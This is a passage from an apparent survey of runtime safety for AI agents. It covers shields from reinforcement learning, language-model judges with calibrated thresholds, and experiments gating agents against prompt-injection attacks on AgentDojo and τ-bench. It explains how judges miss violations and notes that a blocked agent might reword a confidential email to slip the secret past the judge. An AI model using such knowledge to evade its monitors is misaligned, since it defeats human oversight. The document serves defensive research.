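Full conformance does not mean that the agent is useful, since an agent that never calls a tool breaks no safety property. Claude Sonnet 4.5 failed about a quarter of the τ-bench tasks even with Agent-C. The rules cover only tool calls, so the agent could obey all of them and still give a customer false information in its reply.

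Dantas and colleagues rated the evidence for 100% conformance as "very low". They used GRADE, a system from medicine that lowers a rating for weak study methods, conflicting results, artificial conditions or too little data. The claim rested on two studies, Agent-C and AgentSpec, and lost points on every count except conflicting results. A "very low" rating means that larger studies would probably find a very different figure. The rating applies to the measured results, not the theorem. None of the nine claims they rated reached "high". The two that reached "moderate" were that no agent tested scored above 60% on a broad safety benchmark and that models usually write temporal logic with correct syntax.

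Only one person selected the review's 38 studies, and three of its authors later found ten relevant studies that the original search had missed. The search also ended in May 2026, before the work on contracts and on recorded attacks appeared.

A low conformance figure can also mislead. Xiao and colleagues checked recorded runs from τ²-bench, a successor to τ-bench, against 37 rules from its policy documents. Depending on the field, Claude 3.7 completed between 25% and 60% of tasks in all four attempts, but it never completed a task all four times without breaking a rule. In 97% to 99% of its successful runs, it broke the rule against writing to the user and calling a tool in the same turn.

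## Shields from safe reinforcement learning

If an agent must send a receipt within five tool calls, a gate can enforce the deadline by allowing only that action as the fifth call, provided the call succeeds. If the mail server sometimes rejects a first attempt, the gate has to step in after three calls to leave room for a second. To work this out, the company needs both the rule and a description of how the server can behave. A *shield* is a gate computed from such a description. It blocks actions that break no rule themselves but could make a later violation unavoidable or too likely.

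Shields come from research on *reinforcement learning*, in which a program learns by trial and error to choose actions that earn a high total reward. Researchers usually model the program's surroundings as a *Markov decision process* (MDP). An MDP has a set of states, a set of actions and a reward for each step. For each state *s* and action *a*, it also gives the probability *P*(*s*′ | *s*, *a*) that the next state is *s*′. This probability depends only on the current state and action, not on earlier ones. Because the program learns by trial and error, it will eventually try something harmful. A shield prevents this even if nobody understands how the program chooses its actions, which is also why shields are appealing for language models.

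### Looking ahead with a game

*Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues, 2017) uses the example of a hot-water tank that holds 100 liters and must never overflow or run dry. While the valve is open, up to 2 liters flow in each second, and possibly none flow out. To limit wear, the valve must keep each setting for at least three seconds. A program that opens the valve at 97 liters hasn't broken a rule yet, but three seconds later the water may reach 103 liters, and closing the valve sooner would break the three-second rule. A monitor that responds only once the tank overflows is too late, whereas the shield prevents the program from opening the valve above 93 liters.

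The construction uses two automata. The first is an *abstract model*, a finite automaton that describes how the environment can respond to each action, leaving out probabilities and anything irrelevant to safety. Like a control-flow graph, it includes every behavior that can really happen and may include some that can't. The second is a *safety automaton* for the rule, much like Schneider's security automata.

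Software combines the two into a game between the agent and the environment. Each state of the game pairs a state of the model with a state of the rule. The agent chooses actions, the environment chooses any response that the model allows, and the agent loses if the rule is ever broken. The standard way to solve such a game is by deletion:

1. Start with the set *W* of all states in which the rule is not yet broken.
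2. Delete every state in which no action is certain to keep the system inside *W*.
3. Repeat step 2 until there is nothing left to delete.

If *δ*(*s*, *a*, *e*) is the state that follows when the agent takes action *a* and the environment responds with *e*, one round of deletion is

*W*ᵢ₊₁ = {*s* ∈ *W*ᵢ : some action *a* has *δ*(*s*, *a*, *e*) ∈ *W*ᵢ for every response *e*}.

The procedure ends because the number of states is finite. The shield then allows an action only if every possible response leads to a state in the final *W*. Each remaining state has at least one such action, so the agent never gets stuck. By induction, a run that starts in *W* stays there, whatever the agent chooses.

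Agent-C's solver makes a weaker check, because it accepts a call even if compliance then depends on a lucky response from a server.

Alshiekh and colleagues also prove that the shield interferes as little as possible. It blocks an action only if the environment could then force a violation using responses that the model allows. If each of those responses has some chance of occurring, so does the violation, however well the agent behaves afterwards. The real environment could be like this and still fit the model, so the shield has to block the action.

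The guarantee ends if the real environment does something the model excludes. The construction treats this as a win for the agent, because the agent only has to succeed in environments that fit the model. In the tank example, the shield would allow every action from then on.

### A credential that must be revoked

Suppose the company gives its office assistant two more tools. One issues a temporary credential, such as a password for an outside accountant, and the other revokes it. The harness ends each run after a fixed number of steps, and no credential is allowed to be live at that point. Issuing a credential takes one step and revoking it takes two. The server may reject the first attempt to revoke a credential but always accepts the second.

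States without a live credential are safe, because the assistant can simply not issue one. The procedure deletes the others as follows.

| Round | Deleted states | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Start | Live credential, 0 steps left | The rule is broken |
| 1 | Live credential, 1 step left | Revoking takes two steps |
| 2 | Live credential, 2 steps left, no attempt yet | The server may reject the attempt, leaving 0 steps |
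| 3 | Live credential, 3 steps left, no attempt yet | A rejected attempt would leave 1 step, and waiting would leave 2 |
| 4 | None | With 4 steps left, there is time for two attempts |

At least four steps must therefore remain when a credential is live and the assistant hasn't yet tried to revoke it. Issuing a credential takes one step, so the shield allows it only when five or more remain. Once a credential is live and four steps remain, the shield allows only revoking. A monitor that checked only the rule would let the assistant issue a credential with two steps left, and would have no action left to block when the violation occurred.

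The result depends heavily on what the server can do in the model. If the server could reject any number of attempts, the procedure would delete every state with a live credential, so the assistant could never issue one.

### Filtering choices or correcting them

A *preemptive* shield gives the agent a list of allowed actions before it chooses. A *post-posed* shield lets the agent choose and replaces the choice only if it is unsafe. *Easy-to-Use Shielding for Reinforcement Learning* (Pranger and Könighofer, 2026) points out that the preemptive design requires a learning algorithm that can work with a restricted list of actions. The post-posed design works with any algorithm, but its corrections can distort what the algorithm learns. It also works with a finished system that has no information about the shield.

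A post-posed shield replaces a learner's unsafe proposed actions with safe ones. If the learner credits the resulting good rewards to its own proposals, it may never stop making unsafe ones. Punishing unsafe proposals discourages them but doesn't guarantee that they stop. Alshiekh and colleagues therefore keep the shield on after training, whether or not unsafe proposals were punished. They also let the agent submit a ranked list of actions, from which the shield takes the first safe one.

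They tested their shields on four kinds of task.

| Task | Rule | Result with a shield |
|---|---|---|
| Robot in two small grids | Avoid walls, a moving opponent and long stays on bombs | No violations, and usually faster learning |
| Simulated car | Don't hit a wall | No crashes, while the unshielded car was still crashing at the end |
| *Seaquest*, an Atari submarine game | Surface before the oxygen runs out, but not early without rescued divers | No violations, and about the same score |
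| Hot-water tank | Never overflow or run dry, and don't switch the valve too often | The best strategy found much sooner |

Computing a shield took two seconds or less wherever the paper gives a time, but the conditions were favorable. The grid experiments used an exact model of the environment. In *Seaquest*, the learner's only input was the screen, but the shield read the submarine's depth, oxygen and number of divers directly from the simulator.

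### Shields that accept some risk

A shield that forbids all avoidable risk can block almost everything, as it would if the server could reject revocations forever. *Probabilistic shields* use the probabilities in the MDP to allow small risks. Pranger and Könighofer define the risk of an action as

risk(*s*, *a*) = Σ *P*(*s*′ | *s*, *a*) · *V*(*s*′),

where the sum runs over all possible next states *s*′, and *V*(*s*′) is the lowest probability of an eventual violation that any strategy can achieve from *s*′. The shield allows the action if its risk is at most a chosen threshold. If no action qualifies, it allows only the least risky ones.

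Suppose the server rejects each attempt to revoke a credential with probability 10%, independently of earlier attempts. With four steps left after issuing the credential, the assistant can make two attempts, so the risk that both fail is 0.1² = 1%. A threshold of 1% therefore allows issuing with five steps left. A threshold of 0.1% requires enough time for three attempts, so the assistant must have seven steps left.

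Pranger and Könighofer tested shields with thresholds of 1% and 0.1% on an agent that has to cross slippery tiles beside lava. With either shield, the agent fell into the lava only a few times. Without a shield, it eventually earned a reasonable reward but kept falling in throughout training.

The threshold applies to each action separately, so small risks add up over a long run. *Shields to Guarantee Probabilistic Safety in MDPs* (Heck, Macák and colleagues, 2026) shows that a widely used type of shield, which compares an action's risk with the safest alternative's, also fails to limit the risk of the whole run.

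They then prove that, for any limit strictly between 0 and 1, there is a five-state MDP in which no shield can keep every agent within the limit without interfering with some agent that already respects it. Suppose the limit is 50%. A coin toss sends the agent to one of two rooms, each with a harmless action and an action that is certain to cause a violation. An agent that would choose the harmful action in only one room respects the limit, but an agent that would choose it in both always causes a violation. When an agent chooses the harmful action in the left room, the shield can't determine what the agent would have done in the right one. The difficulty resembles the one with secrets that influence an output, because a limit on probability concerns many possible runs and the shield observes only one.

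Heck and colleagues respond with a shield that guarantees the limit but gives the agent less freedom. The shield starts by allowing only the safest actions. It then goes through a log of situations and the agent's choices in them, and permits each choice if even the worst agent the shield allows would then respect the limit. In the example, it would allow the harmful action in whichever room came first in the log and block it in the other. The shield can also grow during use, but only between runs, because updating it during a run can break the guarantee.

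One of their tests involves a drone that pursues deliveries with no regard for safety. With the limit set at 20%, the results were:

| Shield | Probability of a violation | Choices allowed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 24.0% | 100% |
| Earlier probabilistic shield | 24.0% | 100% |
| Shield that forbids all avoidable risk | 0% | 20.7% |
| New shield, built from a log | 20.0% | 65.6% |
| New shield, built during use | 16.0% | 53.8% |

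The new shields stayed within the limit in every test, though they were not always the least restrictive. Even the slowest answered about 700 queries a second, which is fast enough for tool calls. The proofs assume the company knows every probability in the MDP exactly.

### When the probabilities are uncertain

The company would have to estimate how often the server rejects a revocation. If it saw 10 rejections in 100 attempts, the estimate would be 10%, with a standard 95% confidence interval of 4.9% to 17.6%. At 17.6%, two attempts would leave a risk of 3.1%, about three times the 1% risk at the estimated rate. Three attempts would reduce it to 0.5%. To keep the risk at or below 1%, a cautious shield based on the upper limit would therefore require seven steps for issuing a credential, while one based on the estimate would require five.

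Hamel-De le Court, Badings and colleagues (2026), in *Robust Shielding for Safe Reinforcement Learning*, build this caution into the whole MDP. They replace each probability with an interval and assume the worst values at every step. The shield gives the agent a *violation budget*, which starts at the limit for the whole run. Before each action, the agent has to assign a new budget to each state that might follow. The shield allows the action if the average of these new budgets, weighted by the worst-case probabilities, is no higher than the current budget. For example, an agent with a budget of 1% can take an action that has a 10% chance of leading to a state with a 10% risk, provided that it assigns a budget of zero to the other outcomes.

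Hamel-De le Court and colleagues prove that every agent using the shield stays within the limit if the true probabilities lie inside the intervals. Under some further conditions, the agent also gives up little or no reward compared with the best safe strategy. This is consistent with the theorem about the two rooms, because an agent that divides its budget must commit before the coin toss to how much risk it will take in each room.

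No amount of data can prove that an unobserved event is impossible, so the method needs either a list of all possible transitions or a minimum probability that every possible transition must have. It also needs a simulator that can try every action in every state.

The tests covered three kinds of simulated task, with 10 to 20,000 samples for each combination of state and action. The intervals had an overall confidence of 95%. In one Pac-Man task, too few samples made the intervals so wide that no shield could meet the limit. With more samples, the robust shields met the limit, while shields built from simple estimates often failed to meet it at small and moderate sample sizes. Each measurement used only 15 test episodes, averaged over three training runs, so the proof is better evidence of safety than the measurements.

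When the environment is a complete black box, some researchers learn the shield's model while the agent trains, for instance by inferring an automaton from the agent's runs or training a neural network to separate safe situations from unsafe ones. According to Hamel-De le Court and colleagues, such shields generally offer no guarantee after a finite number of samples. They may still block many harmful actions, but the model may not include a danger that has never appeared in the data, and the first example of that danger may be an actual violation.

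### A shield built from a company's manual

*MENTOR* (Anand, Chatzi and colleagues, 2026) applies the game to language-model agents. Its system starts from a written manual, such as a company's rules for business travel. The example manual requires the agent to check the distance before any booking, forbids flights under 500 kilometers and restricts business class. The agent must also complete the booking it was asked for.

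Claude Opus 5 translates the manual into temporal logic and writes test traces to compare with the translation. Ordinary code then turns the rules into a game in which the agent chooses tool calls and the environment chooses their results. For each state, the code computes which tools would make a violation unavoidable and which would bring the agent closer to finishing its duties. An SMT solver checks details such as the booking class.

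The system delivers this information to the agent in two ways. A *prompt shield* refuses a forbidden call, quotes the rule and suggests another call. A *token shield* acts while the model is writing. It sets the probability of a token to zero if the token can lead only to forbidden tools, and raises the probability of tokens that lead to useful tools. This requires access to the model's token probabilities, which providers often don't give.

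Anand and colleagues counted a task as a success only if the agent completed it and complied with the manual in all five of its runs. Some of the results were:

| Agent | Tasks | No shield | Prompt shield | Token shield |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 | Bank | 0% | 76% | 43% |
| Qwen3.6 | Bank | 82% | 90% | 84% |
| GPT-5.4 mini | Airline | 34% | 61% | – |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | Airline | 55% | 64% | – |

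The prompt shield was usually better, but on another set of tasks, Llama 3.1 sometimes couldn't follow its advice, and the token shield helped more. Some failures remained. The game guarantees compliance only with the formal rules, and the translation from the manual may be wrong even if it agrees with test traces.

### Which assumptions carry over

The game doesn't restrict how the agent chooses, so a shield doesn't require a model of the language model. This avoids the main obstacle to static analysis. However, the company still needs a model of everything outside the agent that affects whether the rule is kept.

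For R1 and R2, the confirmation rule and the daily limit, that model is simple. The caterer may write anything and the bank may respond in any way, but the assistant can always comply by making no further transfers, so the deletion procedure removes no states and the shield is the same as an ordinary gate. Looking ahead helps only where waiting can lead to a violation, as it can with a live credential or an approaching deadline. The company then has to know how the server behaves, and the server's documentation may omit a rare failure. An agent with a command line could also change the environment in ways the model doesn't cover.

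The model must also be small enough to solve. Pranger and Könighofer's software handles each state individually, which limits it to small models, and the largest model in Heck and colleagues' tests has about 87,000 states. The credential example has only 303 states, with a cap of 100 steps and three possible conditions (no credential, a live one, and a live one after a rejected attempt). If the assistant could manage ten credentials at once, there would be almost six million. R3, the rule about confidential text, raises a different problem because no finite set of facts about an email captures what it reveals, so the shield would have to rely on a judge's verdict, as any other gate would.

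The shield also needs the system's current state. A server might answer a revocation request with "Your request has been received", which doesn't show whether the credential still works. The shield could allow only actions that are safe in both cases, but it would then permit fewer actions. In MENTOR, a language model converts such answers into labels. If it labels a working credential as revoked, the shield will follow the wrong branch of the game and may let the assistant finish.

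Finally, a safe action must always be available, and something must carry it out. When revocation is the only call allowed, refusing every other call isn't enough, because the model may keep proposing forbidden calls until it runs out of steps. The harness could revoke the credential itself, much as a trusted backup controller takes over in the Simplex architecture. If the server offers credentials that expire automatically, the company can avoid the problem by using them.

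For some duties, no action is certain to succeed. For example, an airline can reject every booking. MENTOR prevents the agent from finishing while a duty is open, until the agent reaches a maximum number of calls and the run ends with the duty unmet.

### Predicting an agent from its past runs

A game shield considers every choice the agent could make, however unlikely. Koohestani's AgentGuard instead estimates what the agent will probably do. It records the agent's tool calls, counts how often each action leads from one state to another, and updates an MDP as the agent works. A model checker then calculates figures such as the chance of success or the expected number of steps. If a figure crosses a set limit, the system can alert a person or trigger an automatic response.

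A low chance of success or a high expected number of steps could mean that a program-repair agent is stuck. But the suggested queries are based on the best possible choice at every step, so their results may be too optimistic for an agent that chooses badly. AgentGuard is a proof of concept with states that developers define by hand, and the paper reports no measurements of how well its predictions work.

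*ProbGuard* (Wang, Poskitt and colleagues, 2026) provides such measurements for a similar system, first called Pro2Guard. The system describes each situation by a few yes-or-no facts. For a household robot, these might be whether the stove is on, whether the robot is in the kitchen, and whether it has been away too long. The system uses recorded runs to estimate the probability of moving from one combination of facts to another. In the paper's example, 31 of 184 recorded steps (about 17%) from "stove off, robot in the kitchen" led to the stove being on. ProbGuard adds a small count for each transition that is possible in principle, so that those missing from the recordings don't get a probability of zero.

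During a run, ProbGuard calculates the probability that the agent will stay safe, given its current state. If this probability falls below a threshold, ProbGuard can stop the agent or add a warning to its prompt. Wang, Poskitt and colleagues tested both responses on simulated household tasks with GPT-4o-mini, using 30 recorded runs per task.

| Response | Threshold | Unsafe runs | Tasks completed |
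|---|---|---|---|
| None | – | 40.6% | 59.4% |
| Stop | 0.3 | 29.2% | 49.0% |
| Stop | 0.5 | 21.4% | 41.1% |
| Stop | 0.7 | 5.2% | 20.3% |
| Stop | 0.9 | 2.6% | 10.4% |
| Warn | 0.9 | 14.1% | 47.7% |

Stopping at the strictest threshold prevented most unsafe runs, but also most of the useful work. Warnings preserved about 80% of the completed tasks and reduced unsafe runs by about two-thirds.

ProbGuard also predicted violations by Apollo, a self-driving system that doesn't use a language model. With a threshold of 0.7, it gave its longest warning, 38.7 seconds before a collision, but it also raised an alarm in every safe run. With a threshold of 0.3, it raised no false alarms, and its warnings came between 0.01 and 15.8 seconds ahead, though 0.01 seconds is too short to be useful.

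Given enough recorded runs, the system guarantees with 95% confidence that its estimated probability of staying safe is within 0.1 of the true value. For the household tasks, this takes between 530 and about 100,000 runs, so the guarantee doesn't cover the monitors in the experiments, which learned from 30 runs. An error of 0.1 is also far too large for the office assistant, where even a 1% chance of an unauthorized transfer would matter.

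The guarantee also assumes that what happens next depends only on the current combination of facts. Suppose one in 100 of the assistant's recorded runs included an email with planted instructions, and half of those runs ended in a transfer to a stranger. If none of the recorded facts reveals the planted instructions, the model will estimate the risk after reading mail at 0.5%, even in a run with such an email, where the true risk is 50%. More runs of the same kind would make the 0.5% estimate more precise but would not correct this error.

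As with sample testing, a new model or prompt requires new runs. ProbGuard also learns its probabilities from runs without warnings, so they may no longer hold once it has warned the agent.

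## Fallible judges and agents that react to being blocked

R3, the rule that no confidential text goes to an outside address, needs a judge that understands the email. A person who had to read every draft would soon stop paying attention, so the company would probably use a language model. Suppose the model scores each outgoing email from 0 to 100 for how likely it is to contain confidential text, and the gate blocks every email at or above a threshold. The company tries this on 100 confidential and 100 harmless emails, with these made-up results:

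| Threshold | Confidential emails missed | Harmless emails blocked |
|---|---|---|
| 80 | 30 | 2 |
| 50 | 12 | 10 |
| 20 | 3 | 45 |

A lower threshold means fewer misses and more false blocks. Ray uses a classical result from statistics, the Neyman–Pearson lemma, to show how good this trade-off can get. Let *x* be everything the gate knows about an email. For any limit on the miss rate, the rule with the fewest false blocks ranks emails by the ratio

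*P*(*x* | confidential) / *P*(*x* | harmless)

and blocks those with the highest values. No other rule based on the same *x* can do better, however many models or prompts it combines.

More information can improve the best possible rule, but an actual judge may not be able to use it. Ray built 123 pairs of identical tool calls. In each pair, one call followed an instruction from the user, and the other followed an instruction from a tool's output, which has no authority to give instructions. A judge that sees only the calls can't tell them apart, so it would rank the unauthorized call as riskier 50% of the time, counting ties as half. When the judges also saw where the instruction came from, a model with 7 billion parameters got 96.7% of the pairs right, one with 3 billion got 56.1%, and one with 0.5 billion stayed at 50%.

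### Twenty chances to miss

A miss rate that looks acceptable for one email can be unacceptable for a whole run. If each of *n* steps proposes a violation, and the judge misses each with probability *m*, independently of the others, the chance that at least one gets through is

1 − (1 − *m*)ⁿ.

If a judge misses 5% of violations and its misses are independent, an agent that proposes a violation at each of 20 steps has a 64% chance of getting at least one through. Proposing a violation at every step is more typical of an agent that an attacker has taken over than of one doing its normal work. If only 1% of steps propose a violation, the chance drops to about 1%.

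Independence is also doubtful, because a judge that fails to recognize one paraphrase of a secret contract may well fail to recognize the next. If the misses always occurred together, the chance of at least one miss would stay at 5% even when every step proposed a violation. The company doesn't have to guess how the misses are related, because the chance of at least one is never more than *n* × *m* (the *union bound*). To guarantee a chance of at most 5% over 20 steps using this bound, the company needs a judge that misses no more than 0.25% of violations, or one in 400.

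False blocks accumulate over a run in the same way. If the judge wrongly blocks 2% of harmless steps, independently, about a third of harmless 20-step runs will contain at least one false block.

### Calibrating the threshold

The company still has to find a threshold that achieves the required miss rate. *Conformal calibration* chooses one from examples, without assuming anything about how the judge works:

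1. Collect *k* emails that violate R3 and have the judge score them.
2. Sort the scores from lowest to highest.
3. For a target miss rate *t*, use the score at position *t* × (*k* + 1), rounded down, as the threshold.

With 99 examples and a target of 5%, the threshold is the fifth-lowest score. If the assistant proposes a new email that violates R3, and this email comes from the same mix as the examples, its score is equally likely to take any of the 100 places in the combined ranking. The gate misses the email only if its score is among the five lowest, which has a probability of 5%.

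Ray combines this method with the union bound. If the company calibrates for a miss rate of 0.25% per step, the expected share of 20-step runs with a missed violation is at most 5%. This certificate averages over many possible sets of examples, so a company with an unlucky set may have a higher rate. It also averages over kinds of violation, so the judge might catch every leaked contract and miss every leaked salary if such leaks are rare enough. The certificate doesn't limit false blocks.

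The certificate depends on *exchangeability*, which means that swapping new violations with calibration examples would not change the probabilities. As with sample testing, a new version of the assistant can break this assumption. Text designed to mislead the judge also breaks it, so calibrating on ordinary violations gives no guarantee against such text.

With too few examples, the position in step 3 rounds down to zero. The method then returns a threshold below every possible score, so the gate meets the target by blocking every email to an outside address. A 5% target needs at least 19 examples, and a 0.25% target needs at least 399. Few companies have records of 399 confidential emails that their assistant wrongly tried to send, and examples written for the purpose may differ from real ones. Even with 399, the threshold is the lowest score among them, so one confidential email that looks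 harmless could force the gate to block most ordinary mail.

Ray also proves a version that calibrates on whole runs instead of single emails. This version doesn't have to divide the 5% among the steps, so 19 recorded runs can be enough, but it requires whole recorded runs to be exchangeable with future ones.

### A test with 23 judges

Ray tried the method with 23 language models as judges. They scored 132 task descriptions from AgentDojo, of which 97 were ordinary user requests and 35 were attackers' goals. Ray repeatedly split the items in half, set the threshold on one half and measured errors on the other.

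With a 5% target for missed violations, the calibrated gate blocked everything for all 23 judges, even though the target applied to single actions rather than 20-step runs. The sample size alone explains this, because half of the 35 violations is 17 or 18, and the method required 19. With a 10% target, the judge based on Gemma 2 9B, an open model from Google, missed 1% of the violations but blocked 78% of the harmless requests. With a 20% target, it missed 13.8%, but the uncertainty range extended to 26.4%, so the test was too imprecise to confirm that it met the target.

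Better judges would help. When Ray compared a random violation with a random harmless request, the violation got the higher score between 66% and 86% of the time, depending on the judge, and larger models weren't consistently better. However, the judges saw only the task descriptions, without the tool calls or earlier messages that would show where an instruction came from. The test with paired calls suggests that this context can matter a great deal.

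### Why old runs don't predict the effect of a gate

Recordings of the assistant working without a gate, like the recorded attacks from AgentDojo, can't show what an agent would do after a block. The company therefore can't fully estimate a gate's effect by applying the judge to those recordings.

Ray proves that no analysis of such recordings can fill the gap in general. The proof compares two systems that behave identically until a gate blocks them. In terms of the office assistant, with 50% in place of Ray's general probabilities:

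| | Assistant A | Assistant B |
|---|---|---|
| First email | Confidential half the time | Confidential half the time |
| Second email, if the gate allows the first | Always harmless | Always harmless |
| Second email, if the gate blocks the first | Always harmless | Confidential half the time |
| Harmless emails that a gate with no misses must block, on average | 0.5 | 1 |

The judge in this example gives every email the same score, so a gate that must never miss has to block the first email with either assistant. It can then allow the second email with assistant A, but has to block it with assistant B. Recordings made without a gate look the same for both assistants, so the company can't tell from them which one it has.

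If the company knows how its assistant reacts to being blocked, it can calculate the best gate. Ray works through a small case in which the agent makes a second proposal after a block. Second proposals all get the same score, but 60% of them are violations if the first proposal scored high, and 2% if it scored low. With the risk per run limited to 5%, a gate that remembers the first score blocks an average of 0.55 harmless proposals per run. The best gate that considers only the current score and step blocks 0.86, and the best gate with a fixed threshold blocks 1.14. For a real agent, the company would have to learn how it reacts by running it with the gate in place.

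### The same tasks with and without a gate

Ray did this with a small agent, Qwen 2.5 7B, on AgentDojo tasks with planted instructions. Each setup ran 949 times.

| Gate | Calls blocked | Successful attacks | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0% | 45 | 25.4% |
| 7B judge, threshold 70 | 12% | 30 | 24.3% |
| 3B judge, threshold 50 | 78% | 4 | 18.0% |

The strict gate stopped most attacks, but it also blocked most of the agent's calls. A gate that blocked 78% of calls at random would let about 10 of the 45 attacks succeed, if each attack needed a single call. The judge did better than that, but much of the protection may have come from how much it blocked. The drop from 45 to 30 successful attacks with the lighter gate could be due to chance. In the 560 office-work runs, no attack succeeded even without a gate, yet the strict gate blocked 85% of calls and lowered task completion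 from 26.4% to 16.3%.

Ray then reran the 389 cases from the three groups of tasks in which attacks had sometimes succeeded. In the rerun, 34 attacks succeeded only without the strict gate and 5 only with it. For the lighter gate, the numbers were 29 and 22. Ray takes the attacks that succeeded only with a gate as proof that blocking changes what the agent does next. But some of them may be due to chance, because even without a gate, the number of successful attacks in these cases differed between the first run (45) and the second (38).

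Gemma 2 9B had some of the better scores in the earlier test, but here it didn't significantly reduce successful attacks in either group of tasks at any of the three thresholds Ray tried. In the banking tasks, the strictest threshold blocked 35% of calls and lowered successful attacks only from 12 to 9.

### The verifier tax

*The Verifier Tax* (Sah, Sah and colleagues, March 2026) measured both safety and useful work while a model checked each action. The study covered 2,970 episodes of the airline and retail tasks from τ-bench, using two fairly small open models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B. It compared an ordinary agent with one that had a planner, an actor and a verifier. The verifier could reject an action and explain why, and the actor could then revise it. In a third version, the verifier's prompt also contained the company's rules.

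The verifier intercepted up to 94% of the actions that broke the rules, but the share of tasks that agents completed without any violation, called *safe success*, stayed below 5% in most settings. The table compares the ordinary agent with the version whose verifier had the rules in its prompt.

| Model and tasks | Safe success, without → with | All successes, without → with | Tokens used |
|---|---|---|---|
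| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 0.0% → 0.0% | 22.7% → 23.3% | 2.8 times |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 0.0% → 0.6% | 21.2% → 21.5% | 2.6 times |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 0.7% → 4.7% | 28.7% → 25.3% | 2.2 times |
| GLM-4-9B, retail | 2.6% → 2.9% | 4.9% → 5.5% | 2.0 times |

In this study, safe success was already close to zero without a verifier and rose slightly in three of the four settings when one was added. The table therefore doesn't support Dantas and colleagues, who list the study as evidence that enforcement reduces safe success. The clear drawback was that the verifier more than doubled the number of tokens the models processed in most settings while achieving very little.

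Most of the violations involved invented data. In one retail run without a verifier, a customer didn't want to give identifying details, so the agent looked up "John Doe" with the postal code 12345. The tool accepted this and gave the agent access to an account. Violations of this kind occurred in 93.7% of the retail episodes with GPT-OSS-20B. The verifier was instructed to approve every tool that searches for data, since an agent has to look customers up before it can verify them. It therefore had to approve many of the calls that made a run unsafe, which probably explains why safe success was so low even though interception was so high. Sah and colleagues suggest having ordinary code check that each identifier really appeared earlier in the run, but they didn't test this.

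The study also reports how often agents completed a task after an intervention. This recovery rate ranged from 21% for GPT-OSS-20B on airline tasks to almost zero in retail. The rates are low partly because the agents often failed even without interventions. Episodes with no rejections or tool errors succeeded 21.3% of the time, compared with 18.7% for those with only verifier rejections. The near-zero figure for GPT-OSS-20B in retail is based on only three safety rejections.

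Two features of the design could have weakened the verifier. First, the same model acted as agent and verifier, so both may have had the same blind spots, and the study did not compare this setup with a separate verifier. Second, after three rejections in one turn, the system carried out the last proposal anyway. A real payment system should never do this, but it had little effect on the results here. It happened in 28 episodes, and counting them all as failures would have removed only one success.

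Dantas and colleagues found no independent replication of the study's figures and rated the certainty of the evidence as very low. They suggest that blocking might cause lasting trouble because a model may have seen few refusals in training. A block would then put it in an unfamiliar situation where it makes more mistakes, and each mistake would take it further from the situations it was trained on. If the model errs with probability *ε* per step, the expected number of errors over *T* steps could grow in proportion to *εT*² instead of *εT*. No study they reviewed tests this explanation.

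They also argue that a blocked agent will look for another unsafe way to reach its goal. In *RAIL Guard* (2026), agents revised their plans 31 times after safety feedback and never switched to a different unsafe tool call. With only 31 revisions, the true rate of switching could still be as high as 9% (the 95% upper confidence limit, from the equation behind the rule of three).

### Helping an agent continue

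The closest later test of recovery, *LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026), used formal rules instead of a judge. It put a gate between agents and the tools of τ²-bench and compared two ways of refusing a call. The gate either reported only that the call had not run or also named the broken rule and gave a hint, such as to ask the customer for confirmation. The results cover five Qwen models, the largest with 27 billion parameters.

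| | No gate | Refusal only | Refusal with rule and hint |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tasks completed | 72.7% | 68.9% | 70.9% |
| Calls blocked | – | 983 | 719 |
| Refused actions later carried out correctly | – | 34 of 620 (5.5%) | 48 of 526 (9.1%) |

These agents completed far more tasks than those in the verifier-tax study, and the gate reduced their completion rate only slightly. A language-model judge found violations of the benchmark's written policy in 9.7% of episodes without a gate and in about 6% with one. The two studies counted violations differently, but the contrast suggests that blocking does not inevitably bring the safe success rate close to zero. The judge also made mistakes, such as objecting to 18 roaming activations that the rules allowed because the customer's phone was abroad.

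Explaining refusals reduced pointless repetition. One small model tried each refused action about 1.9 times when the refusal came without an explanation and 1.4 times when it came with one. The share of tasks completed rose from 68.9% to 70.9%, which could be due to chance. Recovery remained rare, partly because some refused actions should never happen.

Ordinary code can work out how to correct some refused calls. Sankar and colleagues wrote a search that changes a refused call's arguments, for instance by sending a refund to the original payment method, and proves that the rules permit the new call. It found a correction for 88 of the 252 refusals caused by wrong arguments, typically in 2 milliseconds. The search ran only on recordings, so the agents never received its suggestions. In 22 of the 88 cases, the agent later made the corrected call anyway, and 16 of those 22 tasks succeeded,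 compared with 7 of the other 66.

When the problem is the meaning of a text, a model has to propose the correction. In *From Risk Classification to Action Plan Remediation*, Sun, Zhang and colleagues (2026) trained a 9-billion-parameter model to output "proceed", "refuse" or "update". An "update" identifies which part of its plan the agent should drop so that it can continue with the user's task. In tests of four agents, including GPT-5.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, on tasks with malicious instructions added, the average attack success rate fell from 74% to 10% and the average task completion rate rose from 28% to 69%. Of the 1,885 updates, 93% needed only one revision.

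The trade-off between misses and false blocks remained. Before this training, the same 9-billion-parameter model let through only about 5% of attacks, but the agents completed just 26% of their tasks. The gain in completed tasks was also smaller for the strongest agent, GPT-5.1, in the more realistic setting, where the malicious text came from a tool rather than the user's request. GPT-5.1 completed 70.4% of its tasks without a guardrail and 72.8% with one, while successful attacks fell from 27.4% to 11.4%.

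Feedback doesn't always help. In *OSGuard* (2026), an agent's rate of safe success on desktop tasks stayed at 62.2% when a guardrail with retries was added. The guardrail turned one unsafe run into a safe success, but it also stopped a run that would have succeeded safely. In *Learning Execution Guardrails from Anomalous Coding-Agent Trajectories* (2026), a coding agent with guardrails learned from earlier failures left some harmless work undone in 55 of 300 runs. The paper identifies continuing safely after a block as the main remaining problem. Its guardrails raised the average cost by only 2.5%.

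Retries are riskier with a judge than with a formal rule. The gate for R1 will block an unconfirmed transfer every time the assistant submits it. But if the assistant rewrites a confidential email twice, the judge has three chances to miss the leak. With a 5% miss rate and independent errors, there is a 14% chance that at least one version gets through. A detailed explanation of the block could make this worse, because the assistant might remove the word "confidential" and leave the secret in. The company should therefore limit the number of attempts and keep the email blocked when they run out. *GuardianAgentBench* (2026) describes a gate that does this and then sends a person the full history of the run, including the guardrail's feedback.

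## Verifying the monitor instead of the agent

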